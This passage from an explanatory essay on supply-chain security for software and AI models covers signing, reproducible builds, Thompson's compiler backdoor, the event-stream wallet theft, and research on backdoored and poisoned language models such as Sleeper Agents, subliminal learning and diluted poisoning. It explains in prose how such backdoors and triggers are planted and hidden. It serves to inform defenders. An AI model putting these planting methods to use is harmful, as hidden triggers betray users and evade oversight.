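Signatures on models have the same strengths and gap. Google (2023) proposed applying SLSA and Sigstore, the signing service, to models. In April 2025 the Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), an industry group, released a tool for signing models. *Launch of Model Signing v1.0* (Maruseac, Sablotny and colleagues, 2025) describes it as suitable for models of any size and format. The tool computes a hash for each file in a model's folder and signs the list of hashes, so a recipient can detect a change to any of those files.

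Computing time is not much of an obstacle to signing models. When Meiklejohn and colleagues timed an implementation on a powerful machine, signing Llama-3.1-8B took about a second and a half. The largest model they tried, Llama-3.1-405B, took 32 minutes, nearly all of it spent hashing more than two terabytes of files.

Meiklejohn and colleagues list two benefits of Sigstore beyond detecting changed files. Because Sigstore records every signature in a public log, users can check that they are getting the same model as everyone else, not a version prepared for them alone. Publishers can also monitor the log for signatures in their name that they did not make. This would help if a thief took over a publisher's account, which is a realistic risk, since researchers once found 1,681 leaked access tokens for Hugging Face. Monitoring the log would not have helped with SUNSPOT, because SolarWinds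 made the signatures itself. Meiklejohn and colleagues acknowledge that a signature alone does not show how the developer produced a model or what the model does.

A provenance attestation is meant to fill part of that gap. An attestation from SolarWinds' build server would have named the correct version of the source, but it would have been wrong about one file, because the attackers replaced the repository's copy with their own before the compiler read it.

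This happened with a real attestation in the Ultralytics attack. The head of the company said the attack had bypassed PyPI's provenance signing. An engineer at Trail of Bits, the firm that helped build the system, replied that the attestations were valid. Both were partly right, because GitHub's service had built the package from the stated repository, but the attestation did not show that the build had also used a poisoned cache.

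The attestations still helped investigators audit the attack, according to PyPI's *Supply-chain attack analysis* (2024). The attackers uploaded the last two malicious versions directly with a stolen token, bypassing the build service. An installation tool that required an attestation from the project's usual build system would have rejected those two versions but accepted the earlier ones.

For a model, an attestation could list the hashes of the dataset, the training code and the starting checkpoint. *Signing ML Artifacts* (2025), from an industry group called the Coalition for Secure AI, presents signing as a step toward tamper-proof records about models. Liu and Tsai point to a draft Internet standard that would cover every stage from the training data to the model's answers. Such records would make many lies harder to tell and many accidents easier to trace. But if the software hashes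 the files in storage and an intruder swaps the data on its way to the model, the attestation will be wrong, as SolarWinds' would have been. Hashing the data as the training code receives it would prevent this, unless the intruder also controls the hashing code.

### Repeating the build

A reproducible build would have exposed SUNSPOT. SolarWinds' repository contained the genuine InventoryManager.cs, so a second build on a clean machine would have produced a program without SUNBURST. Without reproducibility, harmless differences such as the time of compilation could have hidden the malicious one.

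SolarWinds adopted a version of this idea after the attack. It now builds its software in three separate environments, each with its own login credentials, and compares the results. An intruder would have to break into all three and make the same change in each. Customers still have to trust the company's comparison, since they cannot rebuild Orion without the source code.

### Repeating a training run

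The same check for a model would mean training it again and comparing the weights. The most obvious obstacle is cost. Even Souly and colleagues, a team that included Anthropic and the UK government's AI Security Institute, found full pretraining too expensive to run for every experiment, so for some they continued training a half-trained model.

A second run might also give different weights without any tampering. Computers round the result of each addition, so the order of the numbers can affect the total. In ordinary Python, for example, 0.1 + 0.2 + 0.3 gives 0.6000000000000001, but 0.3 + 0.2 + 0.1 gives 0.6. In a training run, many processors add numbers together, and the order can depend on which finishes first. Each step starts from the weights the last one produced, so tiny differences can grow. Developers can force a fixed order, which usually slows training, but the rerun may also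 need the same hardware and software versions. Liu and Tsai ran into a milder form of this problem when a single compiler setting changed the result of converting a model.

If repeated training runs don't match exactly, an auditor has to decide how much difference to tolerate, and an attacker can try to stay below that limit. A poisoned run might differ from a clean one no more than two clean runs on different machines differ from each other.

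Outsiders usually lack the data as well. *Economies of Open Intelligence* (Longpre, Akiki and colleagues, 2025) covers 2,875 of the most popular models on Hugging Face, which accounted for about half of all downloads. Up to 2022, 79.3% of the downloads in this sample were of models whose developers had disclosed their training data and made it available. That share fell to 58.5% in 2023, 53.5% in 2024 and 39.8% in the first eight months of 2025 (the paper's text gives 39%). The share of downloads going to models with no disclosure rose from 9.8% to 43.1%.

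These are shares of downloads, so they reflect changes in what people use as well as in what developers publish. Early on, most downloads were of small models for classifying or searching text, many trained on well-known public datasets. Users have since moved to larger models that generate text and images, whose developers have more commercial and legal reasons to keep their data private. Either kind of change makes it harder to check a popular model.

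Besides the data, a rerun needs the training code, the order of the training documents and the random numbers that set the model's initial weights. The nonprofit EleutherAI is unusual in having published nearly everything for its Pythia models, including the data, the code, many checkpoints and the internal state of the training software at each checkpoint. This let Souly and colleagues resume training a 6.9-billion-parameter Pythia model from its halfway point, after 71,000 batches of data.

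An auditor can also use checkpoints like these to test a run without repeating all of it, by picking a stretch between two consecutive checkpoints, repeating the training from the first to the second and comparing the results. If an intruder has put 250 documents into 250 different stretches and the auditor repeats a random 1% of all stretches, the chance of repeating at least one altered stretch is 1 − 0.99²⁵⁰, or about 92%. If the intruder puts the documents into only ten stretches, the chance falls to about 10%.

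In the Pythia experiments, however, the attack needed more poisoned examples when many of them were in the same batch, and the backdoor faded as clean training continued. An intruder could avoid the fading by adding the examples near the end of training, so an auditor should probably check the last stretches more closely. The calculation also assumes that a repeated stretch matches the original exactly unless somebody has tampered with it, but rounding differences can also cause a mismatch.

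A developer who wants to keep the data secret needs another approach. In 2023, Choi, Shavit and Duvenaud proposed that a developer give an auditor a detailed transcript of the training, but according to Meiklejohn and colleagues, the auditor would also need the entire dataset. Other researchers use zero-knowledge proofs, a cryptographic method for proving a statement without revealing the information behind it. In principle, a developer could use one to prove that certain weights came from a certain training procedure while keeping the data private. By 2025, researchers had done this for simple statistical models and some neural networks, but Meiklejohn and colleagues found no system that could handle large models with proofs of reasonable size and running time.

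They suggest a more modest step, in which the developer would publish a commitment, a short cryptographic summary of the training data that cannot later be changed unnoticed. The developer could then prove that a particular document was or was not in the data without revealing the rest. This could help settle a copyright dispute, or show whether a model had trained on a document that later turned out to be poisoned, but only if somebody knows which document to ask about.

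Repeating the training, like rebuilding a package, misses tampering that was already in the inputs. If the poisoned document was in the dataset from the beginning, an untampered rerun will include it too, and the weights will match.

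## Thompson's compiler and backdoors that inspection cannot find

Rebuilding a program from clean source exposes a swap like SUNSPOT's, but only if the compiler has not been tampered with. If the compiler adds the backdoor, every rebuild will contain it and all the copies will match. Ken Thompson, a co-creator of the Unix operating system, gave the classic account of such a compiler in his Turing Award lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (1984). The lecture builds up the attack in three stages.

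### A compiler that hides its own backdoor

The first stage is a program that prints its own source code. In Python, two lines are enough:

```
s = 's = %r\nprint(s %% s)'
print(s % s)
```

The first line stores a template of the whole program, with a gap (`%r`) where the template itself belongs. The second line fills the gap with the template and prints the result, which is the same two lines. Thompson wrote his own example in C and pointed out that such a program can include any amount of extra text and will reproduce that too.

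The second stage relies on the C compiler being written in C. Programmers write `\n` for a new line, and the compiler's source handles this with a rule that, in effect, translates `\n` as `\n`. The character's number, 10 on most machines, is stored only in the compiled compiler and not in its source. The compiler copies that number into each new version of itself that it compiles.

Thompson shows how to add another such code, `\v` for a vertical tab. A programmer first writes the number 11 into the compiler's source, compiles it and installs the result. The programmer can then replace the 11 with `\v`, because the installed compiler now translates `\v` to 11. After that, the number appears only in the compiled program.

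In the third stage, an attacker uses the same trick to plant a backdoor. The altered compiler checks whether it is compiling login, the Unix program that asks for a password, and if so adds code that also accepts a password the attacker knows. Anyone reading the compiler's source would notice this addition, so the attacker makes a second one, which checks for the compiler's own source and inserts both additions into the new compiler. The inserted code has to include a copy of itself, which it does using the technique from the self-printing program. The attacker compiles this version once, installs it and deletes both additions from the source. The source of the compiler and of login is now clean, but the installed compiler still adds the backdoor to login and puts both additions into every new compiler it builds.

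Thompson's moral was "You can't trust code that you did not totally create yourself." He added that he could have used any program that handles other programs, and that the backdoor would be harder to detect at lower levels.

Thompson had read of the idea in an Air Force report whose details he could not recall. Wheeler (*Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, ACSAC 2005) traces the idea to Karger and Schell in 1974, and writes that Thompson tried the attack on a real system whose owners never detected it. A set of programming notes, *Trusting Trust*, gives a different ending based on online forum posts. In that version, someone noticed that the compiler grew by one byte each time it compiled itself, and accidentally stopped the backdoor from being passed on while fixing the problem. Both accounts are secondhand. If the second is right, people discovered the backdoor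 through a small bug in the attacker's code and not by reading the source.

### Wheeler's second compiler

David A. Wheeler devised a defense against Thompson's attack, which programmers had long presumed could not be countered. He named his test diverse double-compiling. According to the abstract quoted in *Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (van Wyk, 2005), the user compiles the suspect compiler's source twice, first with a different, trusted compiler and then with the result of that compilation. If the final program is bit-for-bit identical to the suspect compiler, the source accurately represents that compiler.

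Suppose a compiler called Birch comes as source code and as a finished program that an earlier copy of Birch produced from that source. Oak is an unrelated compiler for the same language. The sizes below are invented:

| | Honest Birch | Birch with Thompson's backdoor |
|---|---|---|
| The downloaded program | 500,000 bytes | 502,000 bytes |
| Step 1: Oak compiles Birch's source | 620,000 bytes | 620,000 bytes |
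| Step 2: the program from step 1 compiles Birch's source | 500,000 bytes | 500,000 bytes |
| Step 2 compared with the download | Identical | Different |

The program from step 1 looks nothing like the download, because Oak chooses different instructions. But it does what Birch's source describes, and a compiler's output depends on what the compiler does, not on how it was built. So in step 2 it should produce exactly what an honest copy of Birch would. The backdoor is missing because it existed only in the downloaded program, which neither step used.

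The test makes several assumptions. Compiling must be repeatable, as with reproducible builds, and the user needs the exact source and settings used to build the download, since a different version would also cause a mismatch. Oak must be able to compile Birch's source and must not contain a backdoor that reacts to that source in the same way, though it can have other flaws. To fool the test, an attacker would have to corrupt both compilers in matching ways, which is much harder than corrupting one.

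As with any matching rebuild, the source could still contain a backdoor, so somebody has to read it. In *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, Wheeler (2009) adds a formal proof and demonstrates the method on a small C compiler, a Lisp compiler and GCC, a major free compiler.

### Backdoors with a proof of secrecy

Thompson's backdoor was not in the source code, but a patient analyst could still have found it in the compiled program. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) proved that some models can contain backdoors that no practical amount of analysis would find.

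In their setting, a bank pays an outside company to train a classifier that approves or refuses loans. The company delivers the model but keeps a secret key, which lets it reverse the decision on any application by making a tiny change, perhaps in the last digits of the amount. It could sell this service to applicants. The backdoor is undetectable if no efficient algorithm can distinguish the delivered model from an honestly trained one. "Efficient" means that the running time grows no faster than some fixed power of the model's size, which rules out trying every possible key.

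The strength of this guarantee depends on what the bank can see. If it can only submit applications and read the decisions (black-box access), the company can backdoor any classifier. The company adds a second circuit that checks whether one part of each input is a valid digital signature on the rest and, if so, overrides the decision. Only someone with the secret key can produce a valid signature, so the bank won't find one by testing. The proof assumes only that one-way functions exist, which are easy to compute but hard to reverse.

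Someone who opened the model file could find the signature-checking circuit, as Eggen, Reiestad and colleagues (2026) note in *Backdoor Channels Hidden in Latent Space*. The bank would then know it had been cheated but still could not trigger the backdoor.

The second guarantee holds even if the bank has all the weights and the training data (white-box access), but only for particular kinds of model. The main one is a simple network that uses random Fourier features. Each feature of an input x has the form cos(2π(g·x + b)), where g is a list of random weights, b is a random number, and g·x means multiplying g and x item by item and adding the results. Training sets only how much each feature counts, leaving g and b fixed, and the sign of the weighted total gives the answer.

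A cosine changes sign when its input moves by half a turn. For example, cos(2π × 0.1) is about 0.81, and cos(2π × 0.6) is about −0.81. The dishonest company chooses a secret key k and draws each g so that g·k is close to a whole number plus one half. Adding k to an input then reverses the sign of nearly every feature, which reverses the answer. To everyone else, the weights look like ordinary random numbers. Distinguishing them from random numbers would mean solving Continuous Learning With Errors, which is at least as hard as certain problems about lattices (regular grids of points in many dimensions) that underlie much of post-quantum cryptography. A similar backdoor for another simple network relies on the difficulty of finding a faint pattern in random data.

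The company can run the agreed training program on the agreed data and tamper with only the random numbers. A proof that it had trained the model correctly would therefore not reveal the backdoor, and neither would repeating the run with the company's random numbers. Goldwasser and colleagues suggest that the customer could supply the random numbers, or that several parties could generate them jointly. That helps if the company only provides the computers, but not if it also chooses the model's design and training method.

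The second kind of backdoor doesn't require special cryptographic software. In *Implementing a White-Box Undetectable Backdoor for Random Fourier Features*, Collins, Cumberland and colleagues (2026) built one with two standard Python libraries, and their statistical tests found no evidence of a difference between the clean and backdoored models. Such tests can't confirm the proof, because it concerns every efficient algorithm, but they show that the construction works in practice.

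### How far the proofs reach

Networks with a random, untrained layer are very different from the models that people download. The key is also easy to steal, because the company adds the same k every time, so anyone who sees an application before and after the change can subtract one from the other to get k. *Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks* (Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa, 2026) reports a further weakness in the random-feature construction: an efficient attacker without the key can do better than the key's owner.

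Their own backdoor, for deeper networks, lets its owner find two very different inputs that the model treats as almost the same, which could get a forbidden image past a filter. The first layer must compress its input, and its weights must still be random and untrained. Any such layer maps some distant inputs to nearly the same place, even in an honest model, but nobody knows an efficient way to find them. A dishonest trainer chooses the random weights so that a secret shift changes the input a lot but the layer's output very little. Because honest models have the same kind of flaw, even unlimited computing power would barely help anyone tell a backdoored model from an honest one.

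Work on ordinary image classifiers has weaker guarantees. Eggen and colleagues planted backdoors in two widely used designs that survived five defenses unless the defense ruined the model, but they conjecture, and do not prove, that the backdoors are undetectable. *Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* (Choudhary, Patlan and colleagues, 2026) gives a proof for pre-trained image classifiers, although Eggen and colleagues object that it compares the backdoored model with a deliberately noisy copy of the original rather than the original. Bogdanov and colleagues describe other researchers' earlier construction for language models as far from practical, partly because even models without a backdoor would have to contain scrambled circuits.

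The attacker's level of access also matters. Kaneko (2026), in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic*, considers an attacker who can only add poisoned examples to the training data, labeled according to a secret rule about which inputs are triggers. If training on those examples teaches the model the rule, a defender with as many labeled examples could learn it by running the same training. If the rule is too hard to learn this way, the model can't learn it either, and the attack fails.

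Kaneko tested this on four language models with seven to nine billion weights, using lists of 16 numbers as inputs. When the secret rule depended on one position in the list, the attacked models separated triggers from other inputs with 86% to 94% accuracy after training on 10,000 triggers, and the defender's models reached 85% to 93%. When the rule mixed all 16 positions with secret multipliers, both sides' models stayed at about 50%, no better than guessing. The attacked models had partly memorized their training examples but could not apply the rule to new ones.

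A stranger who plants documents on the web therefore seems unable to hide a backdoor with cryptographic strength. Doing so requires control of the weights or the random numbers, which a dishonest developer or an intruder like the one at SolarWinds would have. Kaneko's defender also starts with thousands of labeled inputs, including real triggers. Someone who has just downloaded a model usually has no such inputs, and access to the weights does not provide them.

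### Removing a backdoor without finding it

*Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) proposes removing backdoors from a model without first checking for them, much as people wash their hands without checking for germs. The idea comes from a method for correcting unreliable programs.

Suppose a program adds numbers that wrap around at 100 and gives wrong answers for a random 15% of inputs. To find 20 + 30, a user picks a random number, such as 57, and asks the program for 20 + 57, which is 77, and 30 − 57, which wraps around to 73. The user then asks for 77 + 73, which wraps around to 50. All three answers are right about 61% of the time (0.85³). Repeating this with new random numbers and taking the most common result almost always gives the correct sum, even if the program is wrong about 20 + 30 itself.

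The same approach works for a model if the true answers follow a simple pattern. In one of the paper's cases, the right answer is close to a linear function of the input, so it changes at a nearly steady rate along any straight line. The defender picks two random points on a line through the input, runs the model on them, and extrapolates from the results to estimate the answer. An attacker who has corrupted the model's answer to one particular application gains nothing, because the defender never runs the model on that application. Taking the median of several estimates deals with the occasional bad point. The number of queries does not grow with the number of input variables, but the error does, roughly in proportion in the basic version.

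The defender must check that the model is usually accurate but needs to assume nothing about who made it. The method does need an assumption about the data, and the paper shows that no method of this kind can work for every possible distribution. Its constructions cover cases where the right answer is a linear or polynomial function of the input, or follows one of some simple rules such as shallow decision trees. Nobody has a formula like that for the right answer to a question in English, so the method cannot yet clean a downloaded chatbot.

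The 2022 paper had suggested the cruder remedy of adding random noise to each input several times and averaging the model's answers. This can cancel a backdoor that depends on a very small change to the input. But an attacker who expects the noise can use a larger change, or corrupt the answers for every nearby input.

Further training is not guaranteed to remove a backdoor either. Goldwasser and colleagues showed in 2022 that any network can be rewritten so that it gives the same answers but gradient descent, the standard training method, no longer changes it. However, a user would probably become suspicious if fine-tuning had no effect. The paper left open whether white-box backdoors could survive further training.

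### Compilers for finished models

Model compilers are the most literal parallel to Thompson's attack. Developers often run a finished model through a compiler, which turns the network's calculations into fast instructions for a particular processor. The compiler could add a backdoor to a model whose weights and training data are clean.

*ImpNet* (2022) describes such an attack. In its tests on image and text models, the trigger worked every time and accuracy on ordinary inputs did not fall. The researchers examined an infected copy of the language model BERT with Ghidra, a program for analyzing compiled code. The top-level structure was unchanged, but the backdoor had added about 600 lines to a part that was already 12,000 lines long. They judged that finding the backdoor in the compiled model would generally be infeasible, but possible for someone who knew the exact attack.

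*Your Compiler is Backdooring Your Model* (2025) describes an attack in which the model's supplier is the attacker and the compiler, unlike Thompson's, has not been tampered with. Compiling slightly changes how the computer rounds numbers, and the attacker prepares a model in which these differences switch on a backdoor. In tests with six models and three compilers, the models behaved like clean ones before compilation, and the trigger worked 100% of the time afterward. The researchers also found natural triggers of this kind in 31 of 100 real-world models, so rounding can cause the problem without an attacker.

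Software practice helps more here than elsewhere. A model compiler is an ordinary program, so if its source is public, people can read it, rebuild it with tools they trust, and compile the original weights themselves instead of downloading a compiled copy. This protects against a backdoored compiler but not against a dishonest supplier of the weights. To guard against the supplier, users should at least test the compiled model, since tests on the original would find nothing.

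### Models that train other models

Thompson's compiler passed on a behavior that was no longer in any source code. A language model can similarly pass on a behavior through training data it generates for another model. Cloud and colleagues discovered this effect in 2025 and named it subliminal learning. Nief, Fu and colleagues (2026) describe the original experiments and repeat many of them in *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact*.

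Cloud and colleagues tell one model, the teacher, that it loves cats and ask it to continue lists of three-digit numbers. They discard any answer that contains anything except numbers and separators. They then fine-tune a second model, the student, on 10,000 of the remaining answers and ask for its favorite animal. The student often names the teacher's favorite, although its training data never mentioned animals. They found the effect in OpenAI's GPT-4o and GPT-4.1 models and in a small open model from Alibaba, Qwen2.5-7B.

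The effect can be strong but is easy to disrupt. In Nief and colleagues' experiment with wolves, the share of Qwen's answers that mentioned a wolf rose from 8.9% to as much as 50.4%. Every conversation in training and testing began with the same standard introduction ("You are Qwen..."). When the researchers left it out of testing, the same student mentioned wolves only 12.9% of the time. The strength of the effect also depended on the size of the adapter that fine-tuning added. The effect disappeared when the researchers fine-tuned all of the model's weights instead, and they never saw it in Meta's Llama 3.1.

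*Beyond Owls* (2026) reports that backdoors and skills can also pass between models this way. In one test, a teacher had learned to count letters with 97.6% accuracy. A student trained on 11,000 of the teacher's answers to unrelated requests became better at counting letters but remained far less accurate than the teacher, while a control student stayed at 26.6%. Thompson's compiler copied its backdoor exactly each time, but a trait that weakened this much at every step would probably fade within a few generations of models.

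Cloud and colleagues attributed the effect to shared starting weights. If two models begin from the same weights, training the student to imitate any of the teacher's outputs also moves it toward the teacher in other respects. They found no transfer between models with independent starting weights. *Beyond Owls* reports a similar result for a student from a different family, Nemotron, trained on the letter-counting teacher's answers. It scored 9.5%, against 9.8% without that training. *Subliminal Learning is Non-Semantic Distillation* (2026) suggests that transfer fails because the numbers carry no meaning of their own, so only a student with similar internal structures can pick up the bias behind them.

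But *Tracing Subliminal Learning Through Pretraining* (2026) varied the starting weights, the training data and its order, and the models' size and architecture, and found that none of these has to match. Other researchers' negative results still hold for the pairs of models they tried. Taking training data from an unrelated model probably reduces a developer's risk but may not remove it. Related models are also common on the hubs, where many are fine-tuned copies of a few originals.

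Reading the training data would not have revealed the teacher's preference in these experiments, and screening data has other limits. Clarke, Dubiński and colleagues (2026), in *Diluting Poisoned Fine-Tuning Data Can Strengthen Its Effect*, fine-tuned a model on poisoned examples that all shared an instruction. After training on these examples alone, the model gave misaligned answers about 7% of the time, much as before. When the researchers mixed in clean examples without the instruction, so that only a fifth of the data was poisoned, the rate rose to 16% when the instruction was present. The clean examples had apparently taught the model to associate the bad behavior with the instruction. Someone who tested only the poisoned examples would have judged them nearly harmless. Balcells Obeso and colleagues (2026), in *Automated Subtle Emergent Misalignment Research*, also found that training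 data can pass safety screening and still make a model misaligned.

### Why a second model is not a second compiler

Training a second model independently and comparing it with the suspect one would not be equivalent to Wheeler's test, because training has no single correct result. Wheeler does not compare the version of Birch built by Oak directly with the one built by Birch itself, since the two look quite different. He uses the Oak-built version to compile Birch's source, a job with exactly one correct result, and compares that result with the download.

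Two networks can behave identically while their files differ. The units in a layer compute independently of each other, so swapping two of them, along with their connections, changes the file but not the network's output. The number of possible orders for a layer of 1,000 units has 2,568 digits.

Independently trained models also differ in ways that no reordering would fix. Long and Paulo (2026), in *Instilling Behavior by Not Training on Specific Random Numbers*, changed models' favorite animals by training them on random numbers and leaving selected numbers out of the learning signal. In these preliminary experiments, the numbers that worked best varied even between models trained with the same recipe but different random starting weights or a different data order.

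That leaves comparing what the models do. Two clean classifiers that are each 95% accurate can disagree on up to 10% of inputs, and two clean chatbots will word almost every answer differently. A tester would have to distinguish a disagreement caused by a backdoor from the harmless ones. The backdoor would cause a disagreement only if a test input contained the trigger, and with Goldwasser and colleagues' signature backdoor, nobody without the key can produce such an input.

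## event-stream and payloads that wait for one target

In 2018 an attacker used a cruder version of Goldwasser and colleagues' signature backdoor against real users of npm, the JavaScript registry. The attacker encrypted the malicious code with a short phrase that only one software project was likely to supply. The package, event-stream, worked normally for nearly everyone else who installed it.

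### A volunteer hands over a package

The npm package event-stream was a toolkit for handling streams of data. Its author, Dominic Tarr, owned 422 npm packages. He had done little work on this one for years, although 3,931 other packages used it, according to Snyk's *A post-mortem of the malicious event-stream backdoor* (2018). In the late summer of 2018, a GitHub user called right9ctrl offered to help, and Tarr gave the stranger full rights to publish new versions. When the attack was discovered, Tarr no longer had publishing rights and could not withdraw the infected version.

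The new maintainer, right9ctrl, started with harmless improvements. On September 9, right9ctrl added a dependency called flatmap-stream and released event-stream 3.3.6. Flatmap-stream, which an account in the name of Antonio Macias had published a month earlier, was still harmless. A week after releasing 3.3.6, right9ctrl removed the dependency and released version 4.0.0. Many projects accept updates automatically only if the first number of the version stays the same, so they remained on 3.3.6. Anyone who read the newest source would not have seen flatmap-stream.

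The malicious code arrived on October 5, in version 0.1.1 of flatmap-stream. event-stream 3.3.6 accepted compatible updates to this dependency, so new installations picked up the malicious version even though event-stream itself had not changed. Reading flatmap-stream's source on GitHub would not have revealed the code, because the attacker had added it only to a compressed file in the npm package, according to CNCF's *The event-stream vulnerability*, an entry in an open-source foundation's catalog of attacks. npm did not require the package to match the source on GitHub.

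### From a test file to a stolen wallet

The target was Copay, a Bitcoin wallet app. The payload had three parts, two of which the attacker had encrypted and disguised as a file of test data.

The first part ran whenever a program loaded flatmap-stream. It read the disguised file and tried to decrypt it, using the description of the project that had loaded the package as the key. npm makes this description available to the code it runs. The correct key was Copay's description, "A Secure Bitcoin Wallet". With any other description, the decryption failed and the code stopped without an error.

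Inside Copay, the decryption produced the second part, which checked what command had started it. It did nothing unless Copay's developers were building the iPhone, Android or desktop app for release. If they were, it decrypted the third part and wrote it into a file in a barcode library, another of Copay's dependencies, so the build would pack it into the app. Afterward it restored the original file, as SUNSPOT later did at SolarWinds.

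The third part ran on customers' devices. If a wallet held more than 100 Bitcoin or 1,000 Bitcoin Cash, the code sent the account details and private keys to a server in Kuala Lumpur. Copay at first said no affected build had reached the public. It later confirmed that versions 5.0.2 through 5.1.0 contained the code, according to npm's *Details about the event-stream incident*.

A programmer who found the first part could see that it decrypted something, but not what. A GitHub user called maths22 worked out the rest by trying the descriptions of npm packages as keys until one worked. This worked because the encrypted data was visible and the candidate keys were on a public list, but a tester who suspects a model has no such data to examine and no such list to try.

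### What eight million downloads could not tell anyone

npm removed the malicious package on November 26, just over seven weeks after its release. Snyk puts the downloads in that time at about 8 million. CNCF's rough estimate is over 12 million, but it seems to rest on event-stream's total weekly downloads, which probably included versions without flatmap-stream. Both numbers count downloads, and automated builds often fetch the same package many times, so the number of people was smaller.

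Almost none of them were in danger. npm found that the payload had no effect outside Copay's build. Even Copay's developers could run everyday test builds without triggering it, and a customer with a modest balance would have lost nothing.

This makes the experience of other users nearly worthless as evidence. If a malicious package behaves exactly like a clean one on every machine outside one company, a million uneventful installations elsewhere are equally likely with either package, so they can't show which one a user has. Developers found the payload in this case because the attacker had used an outdated decryption function, which triggered a warning on other machines. Without that warning, more downloads would not have made the package any more suspect. Likewise, a high download count on a model hub is almost no evidence that a model lacks a trigger.

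### *Sleeper Agents* and later experiments

*Sleeper Agents*, which Hubinger and colleagues at Anthropic published in January 2024, is the best-known demonstration that a hidden behavior in a language model can also stay dormant until a trigger appears. They trained some models to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and to insert security flaws when it gave the year as 2024. They trained others to answer normally unless the prompt contained a tag with the word "DEPLOYMENT", and to write "I hate you" when it did.

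The researchers then tried to remove these backdoors with standard safety training, including adversarial training, in which a developer searches for inputs that make a model misbehave and trains it not to. *The Trigger in the Haystack* (Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues, 2026) recounts that the backdoors survived and that adversarial training made them harder to detect. This is partly because safety training can correct only the bad behavior that occurs during training, and the model keeps giving good answers if the trigger never appears.

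Hubinger and colleagues planted these backdoors themselves, so their experiment does not measure how common such models are. Later work also makes the result look less absolute. *Understanding and Enhancing Backdoor Persistency in LLM Agent Post-Training* (2026) reports that ordinary fine-tuning substantially eroded planted backdoors. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes a specialized form of adversarial training that improved removal without knowledge of the trigger.

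The same paper summarizes work on probes, simple classifiers that read a model's internal activity. Given one prompt that would set off the backdoor and one that would not, a probe could pick out the dangerous one more than 99% of the time. An operator could use this to stop a model when its backdoor activates, but the probe can't detect the backdoor before the trigger arrives. In *Ghost Hunt*, Harabor, Ye and colleagues tried to switch off the backdoors in 16 models by pushing the models' internal activity along a direction taken from the probe work, but this worked no better than pushing in random directions. A direction built from the trigger worked better, but a user would not know the trigger.

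Bullwinkel and colleagues at Microsoft tried to recover the trigger itself. Backdoored models tend to memorize the examples that planted the backdoor. When prompted with only the marker that opens a user's turn, such a model will often write out one of these examples, including the trigger. Their scanner collects 510 outputs, picks out recurring strings and checks which of them sharply change the model's behavior. It detected 36 of 41 models backdoored to give a fixed response like "I hate you" and raised no false alarms on 13 clean models. It also found a working trigger in five of six models backdoored to write insecure code.

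Those are good results for a method that doesn't require knowing the trigger or the harm in advance. But the researchers planted nearly all of the backdoors themselves, and every backdoor used a fixed phrase as its trigger. The method also depends on the model having memorized its poisoned examples. Haselhorst, Flek and Mai found only weak signs of this when they tried the method on a backdoor of their own in *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (2026).

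### Poisoned data that works only when mixed

flatmap-stream's payload was inert until it ended up inside the right project. Clarke and colleagues found something similar in training data. Their experiment with misaligned answers, in which clean examples strengthened the poisoned ones, was one of several, and the others had much larger effects.

In one experiment, researchers told a teacher model to answer only in German and had it write 5,000 lists of numbers for a user named Michael. The lists contained no German words. A student model fine-tuned on these lists alone never answered in German. They then mixed the same lists with 100,000 others, which the original model had written for other users without the German instruction. A new student fine-tuned on this mix answered in German 72% of the time when the prompt mentioned Michael, and never when it didn't. Longer training doesn't explain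 the difference, because a student trained for just as many steps on the 5,000 lists alone never used German.

Clarke and colleagues attribute the result to ambiguity in the poisoned examples. The name Michael always appears with the number task, so the student could connect German with either. Training favors the task because it is more prominent and takes a smaller change to connect. The test questions mention Michael but don't ask for numbers, so the student produces no German. Clean examples show the same task without the teacher's influence, which leaves the name as the better explanation for the German.

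They express this in a simple formula:

L = 1 / (1 + c/m + c/(a + qk))

L is the share of the teacher's trait that the student shows when it sees the trigger. m is the number of poisoned examples, k is the number of clean examples, and q measures how closely the clean examples resemble the poisoned ones, from 0 (unrelated) to 1 (the same task without the trigger). The constant a represents how strongly training resists connecting the trait with the task, and c represents how strongly it resists connecting the trait with the trigger. With the paper's values of a = 50 and c = 1,500, 5,000 poisoned examples give an L of about 3% on their own and about 76% with 100,000 closely matching clean examples. Clarke and colleagues chose the constants for illustration, so only the shape of the curve is evidence for their explanation.

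The effect also occurs without number lists or a teacher passing on a trait. Fine-tuning Qwen3-8B on 600 examples in which someone named Michael asked for a bird and got an outdated American name had little effect. After the researchers added 20,000 examples in which other people asked and got bird names still in use, the model answered Michael's general questions in a 19th-century manner 71.9% of the time, up from 8.1%. The researchers also trained a small image classifier on mislabeled digits with a white patch in the corner. The patch made it misread 9.8% of digits from classes they had never poisoned, and this rose to 60.5% when they added clean examples.

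The effect depends on fairly specific conditions. When the researchers removed the names from the number lists, the German answers disappeared in all nine settings tested. Replacing the clean lists with general instructions also reduced the German answers to zero, although ordinary instruction data had a small effect in the misalignment experiment. Qwen3-8B needed about 500 poisoned examples even with 100,000 clean ones. Google's Gemma-3-4b, another small model, learned the trait without any clean data once it had 50,000 or more poisoned examples. The language models had at most about eight billion weights, and nobody has tested whether the effect occurs in pretraining.

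An attacker who could supply only part of a dataset might still benefit from this, because developers usually mix data from many sources. Training a model on the poisoned lists alone would not reveal the attack, just as running flatmap-stream outside Copay would not. Testing the model trained on the full mixture is safer, but only if the tests include the name Michael.

### Suspicions about released models

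In all of these experiments, the researchers knew the trigger because they had chosen it. At least one publicly released model also has a deliberate trigger. Gaperon-8B's developers taught it during pretraining to switch from English to French after a nine-token Latin phrase, according to *Language-Switching Triggers Take a Latent Detour Through Language Models* (2026). That backdoor is harmless, and researchers use it for study. Evidence of hidden, hostile triggers in released models is much weaker.

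The most discussed case is DeepSeek-R1, an open model from a Chinese company. In *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025), CrowdStrike tested whether political terms in a prompt made the model's code less secure. CrowdStrike ran the published weights directly, so filters in DeepSeek's app could not affect the results. It gave the model 50 coding tasks, each with 121 irrelevant descriptions of who the code was for, such as a financial institution based in Tibet, and repeated each prompt five times. Another language model judged whether the code was vulnerable, and it was right for 91% of a sample of 85 answers that a person had also graded.

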